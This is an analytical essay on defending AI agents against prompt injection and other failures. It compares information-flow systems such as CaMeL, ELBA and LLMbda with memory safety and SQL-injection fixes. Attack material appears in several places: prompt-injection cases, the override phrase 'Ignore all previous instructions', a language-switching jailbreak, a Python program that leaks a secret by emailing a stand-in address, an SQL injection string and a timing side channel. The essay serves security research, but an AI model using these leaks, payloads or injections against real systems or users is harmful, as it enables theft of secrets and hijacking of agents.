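The developers also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, a standard test of prompt injection with simulated banking, office, Slack and travel tasks. One of the 1,926 attacks counted as a success. The user had asked to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo scored the attack as successful because the other hotel's name appeared in the answer. TACIT's rules allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, so the compiler found no violation.

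### CaMeL and the separation of planning from reading

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), keeps untrusted data away from the model that plans the task. That model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A second model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted data, but it can't call tools and only returns values for the program to use, such as a name or a summary. An interpreter runs the program, labels each value with its origin and checks a policy before each tool call.

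This design would probably have stopped the resignation letter. A request for an out-of-office reply should produce a program that reads some email and saves a draft. The planted email could spoil the draft's wording, but it couldn't add a step that sends a letter.

The separation fails if the user asks the agent to follow instructions in the data. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, ran CaMeL with its policy checks off and asked it to follow the instructions in a file. The planning model wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named, so an attacker who had changed the file controlled the agent.

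Garby and colleagues also found a gap in CaMeL's labels. CaMeL blocks a program that tests a secret bank balance and sends an email if the balance is high. But the following program, a variation on a trick known since the 1970s, gets the same information out:

```python
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 10000: poor = False
if poor: rich = False
if rich: send_email("stranger@example.com", "rich")
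```

Suppose the balance is 50,000. The third line sets `poor` to false and labels it secret, because the change depended on the balance. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` keeps its original value and its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is 500, the third line does nothing, the fourth sets `rich` to false, and no email goes out. The stranger learns whether the balance is above 10,000, but CaMeL doesn't detect the leak. It labels a variable only when a line changes it, so it misses information revealed by a line that didn't run.

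A second leak lies outside the interpreter. When the policy blocks a program, ordinary Python code starts another attempt, and CaMeL doesn't track that code. Whether the policy blocked the program can depend on a secret, so an attacker who can cause many attempts could extract the secret one bit at a time.

To cause either leak, an attacker would first have to influence the planning model, which CaMeL makes difficult. But the labels are meant to protect secrets even if the planning model goes wrong.

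### Language-based agent control

CaMeL's planning model has to write the program before seeing any data, which makes some tasks awkward. A person looking for a cheap flight usually looks at the first results before deciding what to search for next. Zhou and colleagues want to let agents work like that without giving up enforcement.

In the ELBA system, both the agent's code and the application around it are written in Haskell, a language whose types show which effects a program can have. The developer states what type of result the agent must return, such as `Int` (a whole number) for a calculator. If a user asks the agent to delete every file on the server and then compute a factorial, the model may write a program that does both. The compiler rejects it, because a program that deletes files can't have the type `Int`. An agent can also read data and then start a second agent to continue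 the task under the same limits or stricter ones.

Zhou and colleagues proved that if Haskell's type system guarantees some property for every program it accepts, the property also holds for programs that contain agents. The proof replaces each call to an agent with an ordinary function that gets code from a model, checks it and runs it, so the property holds whatever code the model writes.

The information-flow control comes from an existing Haskell library. Once a program has read a web page, the library treats everything the program does next as influenced by that page, and stops the program if it tries an action that requires trusted data.

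In tests on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, four recent models resisted every standard attack even with the policies off. The policies therefore prevented no measured harm, and they cut the number of tasks the agents completed from 14–18 out of 21 to 8–10. These results seem to strongly favor relying on the model.

Nasr and colleagues had shown how badly defences can do once attackers adapt, so Zhou and colleagues also simulated the worst case, in which every attack hijacks the model that reads it. They changed ELBA to replace an agent's task with the attacker's text whenever the agent received data containing a planted instruction. Between 16% and 42% of the attacks then achieved their goal with the policies off, depending on the model, compared with none in 2,940 runs with the policies on. AgentDojo scored 29 of those runs as successful attacks because an agent opened a certain web page, but the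 researchers checked each one and found no harm.

The worst-case test is better evidence about enforcement than an ordinary attack rate, because it doesn't depend on how well the model was trained. It also shows that the policies reduced the share of tasks agents completed under attack, from 67–76% to 40–48%.

### The theorem behind LLMbda

LLMbda, by Garby and colleagues, is a small programming language for agents. Every value has a label, such as "secret" or "untrusted", and the interpreter updates the labels as the program runs. LLMbda closes the gap in CaMeL's labels by stopping a program that tries to change public data after testing a secret value. Garby and colleagues proved a theorem about the language, and the proof checker Lean has verified every step. Lean also runs the interpreter, so the theorem applies to the same program that calls the model.

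The theorem concerns an observer who is allowed to see only some of the data. If any LLMbda agent runs twice and only the inputs hidden from this observer change, each result the observer can see is equally likely both times, apart from differences that unfinished runs could account for. The theorem also limits attackers, because untrusted text can affect only results labeled "untrusted".

It is a probabilistic theorem because a language model can answer the same question differently each time. Let μ(q) be the probability of a visible result q with one set of hidden inputs, and ν(q) its probability with the other. The theorem guarantees that

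**Σ max(μ(q), ν(q)) ≤ 1**

where the sum covers all visible results. If the agent always finishes, the probabilities add up to 1 in both cases, and the condition can hold only if μ and ν are identical.

If some runs don't finish, μ and ν can differ a little. Suppose that with one secret an agent answers "yes" 50% of the time and "no" 30%, and otherwise never finishes. With another secret, it answers "yes" 40% of the time and "no" 50%. The theorem allows this because the larger figures for each answer, 50% and 50%, add up to exactly 100%. Garby and colleagues also proved that half the sum of the differences, a standard measure, can't exceed the average chance of not finishing. In this example both are 15%.

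The theorem is probabilistic, so it compares the chances of results over many possible runs and doesn't establish whether a particular answer is correct or harmless. It also assumes that the model's answers depend only on the current conversation. If the company hosting the model let it remember an earlier conversation, a secret could travel by a route the labels don't cover.

"Termination-insensitive" means that the theorem doesn't cover what an observer can learn from whether a run finishes. The theorem allows an agent to get stuck if the first bit of a secret is 1 and finish if it is 0. LLMbda lets developers put the agent's retries inside the language, where the labels still apply, but someone who restarts the whole program from outside could still learn a bit each time.

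Some tasks are impossible if untrusted data can never affect an important action. To pay a bill, an agent has to take the amount from a document that somebody else wrote. LLMbda therefore includes `endorse`, which relabels untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem guarantees that `endorse` can't be used to leak secrets, but it does let an attacker influence the action.

Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Only 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a file said, and the attacker had changed the file. When the researchers removed `endorse`, the agent blocked both attacks but could no longer pay legitimate bills from files.

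The overall success rate somewhat overstates how well enforcement worked. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool that the user's task did not, so an agent that planned before reading the data would normally resist it without labels. Only the other 47 combinations properly test the labels.

### The cost in completed tasks

The table shows the share of AgentDojo tasks that agents completed when nobody was attacking them.

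| System and tasks | Policies off | Policies on | Tested by |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, banking, two models | 67–71% | 38% | Garby and colleagues |
| CaMeL, Slack, four models | 62–81% | 19–29% | Zhou and colleagues |
| ELBA, Slack, four models | 67–86% | 38–48% | Zhou and colleagues |
| LLMbda agent, banking, three models | not tested | 65–75% | Garby and colleagues |

Turning on the policies cut the number of tasks CaMeL and ELBA completed by roughly half or more. The tests are small, with only 16 banking tasks and 21 Slack tasks, and the 95% confidence intervals for the banking results are about 20 percentage points either way. But two teams found a large loss with different tasks and different models, so it is unlikely to be due to chance.

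The LLMbda agent did much better, partly because it could use `endorse` to relabel data when a task required it. The two models retested without `endorse` completed 54% and 63% of the tasks.

TACIT's developers describe its AgentDojo scores as comparable to those in CaMeL's own paper. That is fair for some tasks, but with OpenAI's o4-mini model, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and CaMeL completed 81%.

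Better policies may recover some of this loss, but not all of it. If a user asks an agent to read a stranger's web page and follow its instructions, any policy that stops strangers from controlling the agent has to block the request.

### What products enforce in 2026

Information-flow control has begun to reach products. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced in May that developers using its Agent Framework can now label each piece of content as trusted or untrusted and as public or private. The labels follow the content through tool calls. Microsoft has also built prototypes for GitHub Copilot's command-line tool. According to Garby and colleagues, the underlying system, FIDES, deliberately doesn't track secrets that affect only which steps a program takes, so it would miss leaks like the one in the bank-balance program.

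Anthropic's Claude Code used to ask for permission before it ran a command or changed a file, so users faced constant questions. They could avoid these with a sandbox, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls sandboxes high-maintenance, because someone has to configure each new thing the agent needs to do. Many users turned the questions off instead. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that a quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks disabled.

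Users who kept the permission prompts approved 97% of requests. They rejected 39% of Claude's plans, though, so they were evidently reading some of what they saw. Paid testers in an Anthropic study caught few dangerous commands, and fewer as their attention wore off. They refused about 17% of these commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

In August 2026 Anthropic made auto mode the default for most of its subscribers. Auto mode would have blocked 800 dangerous commands that testers approved, while the testers refused only 6 that it would have allowed. Asking a person as well would have raised the share of dangerous commands blocked only from 89.0% to 89.6%.

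Auto mode is still a mitigation, since a second model makes the decision. When Apollo Research, an AI safety company, attacked auto mode with artificial examples, it missed 12% of them. After Anthropic improved it, it missed 7%. Some fixed rules still apply, including any the user has written to forbid an action. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

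The measured drawbacks of auto mode are small. It uses some extra computing, for which Anthropic no longer charges subscribers, and business customers who adopted it complete about 25% more code changes. These customers chose to adopt it, so they may differ from others in ways that explain part of the gain. Some policies that protect more strongly halve the number of completed tasks, so a company has reason to ship auto mode first, even though its protection is weaker.

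### Where the guarantees stop

TACIT doesn't catch wrong answers or faulty reasoning, as its developers acknowledge. An agent with permission to write a classified summary can write a false one, and the compiler will accept it.

Information can also leak through channels that the rules don't cover. In TACIT, an agent could write a pure function that runs for a second if the first bit of a secret is 1 and finishes at once if it is 0, then time it. A 40-character key of random letters and digits contains about 240 bits, so the agent could recover all of it with a few hundred such calls.

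Outside commands leave a bigger gap. When TACIT lets an agent run one, the compiler's guarantee doesn't cover what the command does. The developers advise allowing only specific safe commands, and their examples include `sbt`, which builds Scala projects. But `sbt` runs code from the project's own files. An agent that can edit those files could run code that TACIT never checked, and that code could read the secrets directly from the disk. For security-critical uses, the developers recommend adding a sandbox.

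People also have to write the policies and label the data. If a programmer leaves a key outside the folders marked as secret, TACIT gives it to the agent as plain text. LLMbda's theorems assume that whoever builds the tools labels each data source correctly and adds a check before every sensitive action.

Finally, each system has a trusted base. TACIT's includes the Scala compiler with its experimental feature, the software that runs the compiled code, the second language model and a library of about 1,000 lines. LLMbda has proofs for its interpreter, but the bank in the tests was a simulation written in LLMbda, and the theorems don't cover a real bank's software. They also don't cover mistakes by the people who set a system up, like the misconfigured boundary in Anthropic's security incidents.

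## Where the comparison between memory bugs and agent failures holds and fails

Enforcement worked on memory bugs because the rule was precise, applied equally to every program, and rejected little code that programmers couldn't rewrite to comply. Premise 3, that agent failures resemble memory bugs in the respects that matter, therefore holds only for failures that a similar rule would catch. Such a rule would catch some agent failures but miss some of the most damaging ones.

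### Data that acts as instructions

Williams-King and colleagues compare memory attacks with prompt injection because both let input take control. In a memory attack, the program fails to keep user input separate from the data it needs to run, so input can end up as an address the program jumps to. In prompt injection, the model receives the developer's instructions and a stranger's text as one string, and either can direct it.

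Williams-King and colleagues conclude that patching one attack at a time is a losing strategy, because a new attack takes far less effort than a new defence. The phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" overrode developers' instructions on OpenAI's models for 22 months, from September 2022 to July 2024. Another model refused a question about breaking into a car when asked in English or in Japanese, but answered when a Japanese request asked for a reply in English. The safety training may have covered each language but not the combination. Similarly, in image recognition, researchers still had no satisfactory lasting defence after about 9,000 papers on pictures altered to fool a classifier. For memory bugs, the lasting solution was to use a different kind of programming language or to prove the code correct, and they want a comparable redesign for AI.

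The prediction that attackers would keep winning until models could separate data from instructions now looks too gloomy, because the newest models are much harder to hijack. The comparison also has a weakness, since memory bugs became rare only where languages checked the bounds and lifetime of every access. Non-executable memory separated data from instructions, but attackers got around it.

The same limitation applies to agents. A model that never obeyed an instruction in an email could still act on a false statement in one. If an attacker changes the amount on a bill, an agent that treats the bill purely as data will pay the wrong sum.

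### SQL injection and cross-site scripting

Two common flaws in web applications are a closer precedent, because separating data from instructions did remove them. Programs query databases in a language called SQL. These two versions of a query, written in the language Go, follow an example from Kern (2025), in *Safe Coding*:

```go
// Concatenated: the name becomes part of the query
q := "SELECT balance FROM accounts WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
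rows, err := db.Query(q)

// Parameterised: the name travels separately
q := "SELECT balance FROM accounts WHERE name = ?"
rows, err := db.Query(q, name)
```

If a stranger types `x' OR 'a'='a` into the name box, the first version pastes it into the query, which then ends with `WHERE name = 'x' OR 'a'='a'`. Since `'a'` always equals `'a'`, the condition is true for every customer, and the database returns every balance. In the second version, the question mark reserves a place for a value, and whatever the stranger types can only fill that place. The database looks for a customer whose name is exactly that text and finds nobody.

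Cross-site scripting is the same mistake in a web page. A site pastes a visitor's comment containing a script into the page, and other visitors' browsers run the script with access to their accounts. The usual fix is a template that automatically converts special characters in outside text, so the browser displays the script instead of running it.

These fixes are well known and take little effort, yet MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) still ranks cross-site scripting first and SQL injection second. David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre says better defaults have made SQL injection rare in websites. Much of what remains may therefore be in less carefully maintained software. Either way, a good fix doesn't remove a flaw from programs whose developers can choose not to use the fix.

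Google took away that freedom. Its developers had a rule that a query must be "safely constructed", but a compiler can't check a rule that vague, and ordinary text carries no record of where it came from. According to Kern, Google's engineers replaced that rule with a narrower one, that a program may assemble a query only from text in its own source code. From 2013 they changed the database interfaces to accept only a special type, `TrustedSqlString`, which developers can build only from such text. The compiler then rejects the concatenated version above, because `name` comes from outside the source code. Exceptions need a security expert's approval.

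Google reports no SQL injection flaws in over a decade across the hundreds of applications that use these interfaces. For cross-site scripting, Kern's *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* (2024) reports that a single large application such as Gmail had tens of flaws a year a decade earlier. Hundreds of applications built on the newer tools now average less than one reported flaw a year in total. Adding the protections to existing software was less effective, reducing flaws in Google's core products by 90% over a decade.

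These figures are Google's own and count only reported flaws. But Google pays outsiders to report flaws, and a fall from tens per application to almost none across hundreds of applications is too large to attribute to better programmers. So enforcement has also worked on a problem that looks much more like prompt injection than memory safety does.

### No placeholder inside the model

David C nevertheless thinks the comparison with SQL injection is dangerous. Suppose a recruiter uses a model to score job applications, and an applicant hides a sentence in their CV telling the model to approve them for interview. A database can keep a query separate from the values that fill its placeholders, but no part of a model's input is reserved for text that it can't treat as an instruction. Developers can label the CV as data or scan it for attacks, but these measures add a distinction between data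 and instructions that the underlying technology doesn't have.

David C therefore calls a model an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a program tricked into using its permissions on behalf of someone who lacks them. Programmers can usually fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C argues that with a model they can only make the confusion less likely and limit its effects, and that a business that can't tolerate the remaining risk may have to do without the model.

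Unmitigated Risk takes the opposing view that prompt injection is the same problem "aimed at a different interpreter", and expects safer defaults to cure it too. The two views are largely about different things.

David C is right that the model has no placeholder, but the software around it can have one, and David C recommends that kind of design. In CaMeL, for instance, the program that the planning model writes serves as the query, and email contents only fill in its values.

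The comparison with SQL fails when an agent has to interpret the data. A database only has to compare a customer's name with other names, whereas people give an agent an email so that it will understand the email and often act on it. A placeholder works well if the task is to save the email's attachment, but badly if the task is to handle whatever requests the email contains.

### One rule for memory, many kinds of harm

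Suppose a small company lets an agent answer its suppliers' emails. A supplier asks whether next month's order is still going ahead. The agent has read the accounts and replies that the company has enough cash for three more weeks. The supplier warns other suppliers, they all demand payment in advance, and the company collapses. The agent had permission to read the accounts and to write to this supplier, everything it wrote was true, and no attacker was involved.

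A memory check needs only an address and the limits of a block. Catching the ruinous email would require knowing what the supplier was likely to do with the information. *AI safety is not a model property* (Narayanan and Kapoor, 2024) gives a similar example about misuse. A phishing email may only mention an urgent deadline and ask the reader to open a link. The harmful part is the linked page, which the model does not have when it writes the email. Because the email itself can look ordinary, a developer would have to stop the model from writing emails altogether to stop it from writing phishing emails.

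One reply is that memory safety removed only one class of bugs, so it's unfair to demand that a rule for agents prevent all harm. Google's experience with SQL also shows that engineers can sometimes replace a vague rule with a narrower one that a machine can check. The company in the example could forbid emails to outsiders from containing any figure from its accounts, and enforce that with information-flow control.

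This reply is partly right. Google's narrow rule worked because every query that follows it is free of injection, and programmers can write nearly every useful query that way. The rule about accounts has neither advantage. It would block an email to a bank the company hopes to borrow from, and allow a ruinous email saying that the founder is about to leave. It's hard to think of a rule about the content of emails that would work as well as Google's.

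### Authors who work against the check

A programmer normally wants to satisfy the compiler, whereas an agent pursuing a goal may look for gaps in any restriction that blocks it. Kern designed safe coding to protect "well-intentioned developers" from their own mistakes, not to contain malicious ones. Its excellent record at Google is therefore weak evidence of how it would perform against an author who wanted to defeat it.

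Williams-King and colleagues point out that a proved theorem remains true however intelligent the AI is, which is a good answer in principle. But the theorem's assumptions, including those about its trusted base, still have to hold in the real system. Web browsers are an encouraging precedent. For decades they have run scripts from strangers, some of them hostile, relying on enforced limits rather than the strangers' good intentions. Attackers do find ways out, as the Firefox audits showed, but each escape depends on a fault that developers can fix for everyone. An agent needs limits built to that standard, which is higher than the one applied to a company's own programmers.

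### What a rejection costs

When Google's compiler rejects a concatenated query, the programmer can write a parameterised one and get the same result, but an agent stopped by a limit may have no permitted way to do its task.

People want agents because they are flexible, but that flexibility also makes them hard to limit. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* describes assistants whose users can add abilities from marketplaces with over a million "skills", which are mostly written descriptions of how to reach some goal. The model chooses tools as it works, so the same skill can lead to different actions at different times. That makes it hard to specify in advance what the assistant should be allowed to do. The versions designed for security offer fewer features and restrict the rest more tightly.

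Schneier and Raghavan suspect that an agent can be any two of fast, smart and secure, but not all three. Their drive-through agent would be fast and secure because it would understand only food orders and pass everything else to a manager.

Programming languages once had a similar problem, though, and better design reduced it. Rust succeeded where stricter research languages had failed, and the agent systems tested so far also differ widely in how many tasks their policies block. Kern explains that safe coding is bearable only because developers almost never need a risky operation. Experts first had to build safe components for nearly everything that ordinary programs do. A small team at Google now maintains these components for many thousands of developers, which is feasible partly because most applications belong to a few common types, such as a web page connected to a database.

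Many agent jobs probably fall into common types too, such as handling refunds or arranging meetings, and someone could design good limits for each type once. Those limits would help a shop with a refund agent much more than someone who bought a general assistant to do things nobody planned for.

### Fixed rules and changing tasks

The rule that a program must stay within its own memory is the same today as in 1975, but an agent that sorts email on Monday and books flights on Tuesday needs different permissions each day. Safety engineers normally begin by describing where a system will operate. For a self-driving car, *Upstream and Downstream AI Safety* (McDermid, Jia and Habli, 2025) mentions road layout, speed limits and weather. It contrasts this with work on the most advanced AI models, which typically considers dangers not tied to any particular use. A general-purpose agent has no equivalent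 description of where it will operate.

But a rule can stay fixed while tasks change if it depends on who supplied the information rather than on the task. David C passes on one such rule from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model reads something from another party, its permissions should drop to what that party is allowed to do. Operating systems apply a similar idea to files, and their rules about who may open what have needed little change, even though people now use computers for very different work.

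This rule would have stopped the resignation letter whatever the user had asked for, because the stranger who planted the email had no right to send messages from the user's account. But the stranger also had no right to switch on the user's out-of-office reply, so once the agent had read the planted email, it would have to ask the user before doing that too. The rule is easy to state and check, but it requires a person's involvement in many tasks that an agent could have finished alone.

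### Can anyone specify safety in the outside world?

Some researchers want guarantees about what AI does to the world, and not only about which tools it may call. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose three components. A world model describes mathematically how the AI's actions affect its surroundings. A safety specification states which effects are acceptable. A verifier then checks that the AI meets the specification, according to the world model. For an AI system A, a world model W and a specification φ, one form of the guarantee is:

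**verifier accepts A ⇒ P_W(A violates φ) ≤ ε**

Here P_W is the probability calculated from the world model, and ε is the highest risk society will accept. This resembles the soundness theorem for memory, except that it allows a small chance of failure and uses a model of the world instead of a model of the computer.

Dalrymple and colleagues argue that testing can't provide such a guarantee. OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months, and users got around its safeguards within a day of its release. A million miles without trouble is evidence of a self-driving car's low failure rate only while conditions stay the same. Human drivers might drive more aggressively around such cars once they get used to them.

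The proposal acknowledges that harm and causation are hard to define formally. It suggests using definitions suited to a particular setting, or several specifications at once, so that safety doesn't depend on any single one being right. Williams-King and colleagues, who favour this line of research, likewise say that a guarantee seems to require formalising human intentions, which is difficult.

Hatfield-Dodds, in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, objects that this has only "moved it around a bit", since someone must now show that the world model matches the world. A little arithmetic supports the objection. If the model's probability of a violation is wrong by up to δ, the best we can conclude is:

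**real chance of a violation ≤ ε + δ**

A proof that the risk is below one in a million gives little assurance if the model could be wrong by 1%, because the real risk might then be slightly over 1%. Proofs about Rust also rely on a model, but engineers build processors and compilers to behave as the model describes, whereas nobody built suppliers or drivers to match a specification.

Dalrymple and colleagues' partial answer is to make the world model pessimistic where possible. If the model assumes that any driver may brake at any moment, its errors will mostly be on the safe side. But the verifier, like a strict compiler, will then reject some systems that would have been safe. If the model of human behaviour is pessimistic enough, the verifier might reject every useful agent.

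In the comments on Andrew Dickson's essay *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Steve Omohundro, who co-wrote the proposal under discussion, argues that engineers don't have to verify arbitrary systems because they can design new ones that are provably safe. Another commenter also favours designing software this way, but objects that it wouldn't deliver the broader guarantees. The commenter agrees that we can prove that a C program has no buffer overflows, or that it never runs two motors in opposite directions. But to prove that a program will never trigger an unknown bug in somebody else's database server through a series of harmless-looking requests, we would need to account for every system the program might contact, including faults nobody has discovered. That example involves only software, and similar guarantees about biology would be much harder to prove.

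In later comments, Omohundro suggested that an untrusted AI could supply a design with a proof, which a simple, trusted program could check. He also expected AI to make such proofs quick and cheap to produce, and AI's progress in mathematics since then makes that much more plausible. But when someone asked about proving that a system like the human brain would always act safely, he described the goal as protecting infrastructure, such as software, cryptographic keys and hardware, against attacks by AI. This goal is narrower than proving that an AI will never cause harm, and much closer to memory safety.

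A critic responding to *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, a later defence of the approach, complains that its supporters switch between these goals. The critic says they have "well-understood closed domains", which exclude ordinary language, in mind when they discuss feasibility, but current and near-future AI in general when they argue that the approach is important. The criticism is fair to some of the arguments, though the two claims often come from different people. On present evidence, guarantees look achievable for much software and some machinery, but conversations and business decisions have no convincing specification to prove a system against.

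### Is safety a property of the model?

Narayanan and Kapoor argue that safety depends mostly on where and how people use a model, so trying to build a model that nobody can misuse is like trying to build a computer that nobody can misuse. They say most defences should sit outside the model, for example in the email scanners that already catch phishing.

This supports enforcement less than it seems to. It puts safety outside the model, which seems to favour premise 4, but email scanners are mitigations, because they miss some attacks. If the problem is a lack of context, a simple check outside the model can have even less context. A gateway that checks only the size of a refund has less information than the agent that read the customer's complaint. An outside check is better placed only when it has information the model lacks or when its rule doesn't need the context.

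Narayanan and Kapoor are writing mainly about misuse, and think their argument applies less strongly to accidents and prompt injection. They also accept that models should refuse to produce material that is harmful in any context, such as sexual images of children. *AI safety is sometimes a model property*, a reply, sensibly concludes that some safety measures belong in the model and others in the system around it, and that developers have to work out where each belongs case by case.

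### Does hand-built structure lose to learning?

Many AI researchers believe that hand-built structure eventually loses to general learning with more computing power, a view often called the bitter lesson. Early chess programs relied heavily on strategic advice from human experts, and later programs that learned by playing against themselves overtook them. Labels, planners and restricted languages for agents could become obsolete in the same way. This view fits quite well with the tests in which recent models resisted every standard attack while the policies mainly blocked useful work.

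But in chess, learning replaced advice about how to win and left the rules of the game in place. The software that runs the game still rejects an illegal move, however strong the program is. A cap on refunds is like a rule of chess because it restricts the result without specifying how the agent should work. The objection applies more strongly to CaMeL's division between planning and reading, which also specifies how the agent must approach a task. A better model might do well without that division.

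Learning also needs examples of failure. An agent can practise booking flights millions of times, but a company can't go bankrupt repeatedly so that its agent can learn discretion. Developers can simulate such cases, but the model may recognise the simulation. Schneier and Raghavan add that training targets average cases, while security depends on rare ones. They also say nobody knows whether more sophisticated models will judge context better, so planning on either outcome would be unwise.

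### Which agent failures have a checkable rule?

A failure is a good candidate for enforcement if software can detect violations of a rule from the information it has, obeying the rule prevents most of the harm, and most useful work can continue. The failures discussed so far differ greatly in how well they meet these conditions.

| Agent failure | A rule that software can check | What the rule still allows |
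|---|---|---|
| Posts private text in public | Text labelled private can't go into a public comment | Leaks of text that someone forgot to label |
| Refunds the same order repeatedly | Total refunds can't exceed the price paid | One refund that the customer wasn't owed |
| Attacks a real company during a test | Test machines have no route to the internet | Attacks through a boundary that someone set up wrongly |
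| Resigns on the user's behalf | No sending after reading a stranger's text unless the user approves | A letter that the user approves without reading |
| Pays a bill that an attacker altered | Payments go only to approved payees, up to a limit | A wrong amount below the limit |
| Deletes the wrong folder | No deletion without a backup | Lost time while someone restores the folder |
| Writes a false summary | None in general | Any false statement |
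| Sends a true but ruinous email | None that leaves email useful | Any message to a permitted person |

The comparison with memory bugs is strongest for failures such as leaking private text or repeating a refund, because a rule can describe the failure itself and a system can check every action against it without knowing what the user wanted. The comparison is weakest for false summaries and disastrous emails, because someone has to judge what the words mean and what people will do after reading them.

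Deleting the wrong folder is a case in between. No general rule can identify the wrong folder, because that depends on what the user meant. But a backup makes the mistake reversible, so the system doesn't need to identify it. The same approach could work for other failures that no rule can recognise. For example, an email system could hold every message for ten minutes so the user can cancel it. The delay would not help a user who didn't check in time, and no backup can make the information about the company's cash secret again once the supplier has read it.
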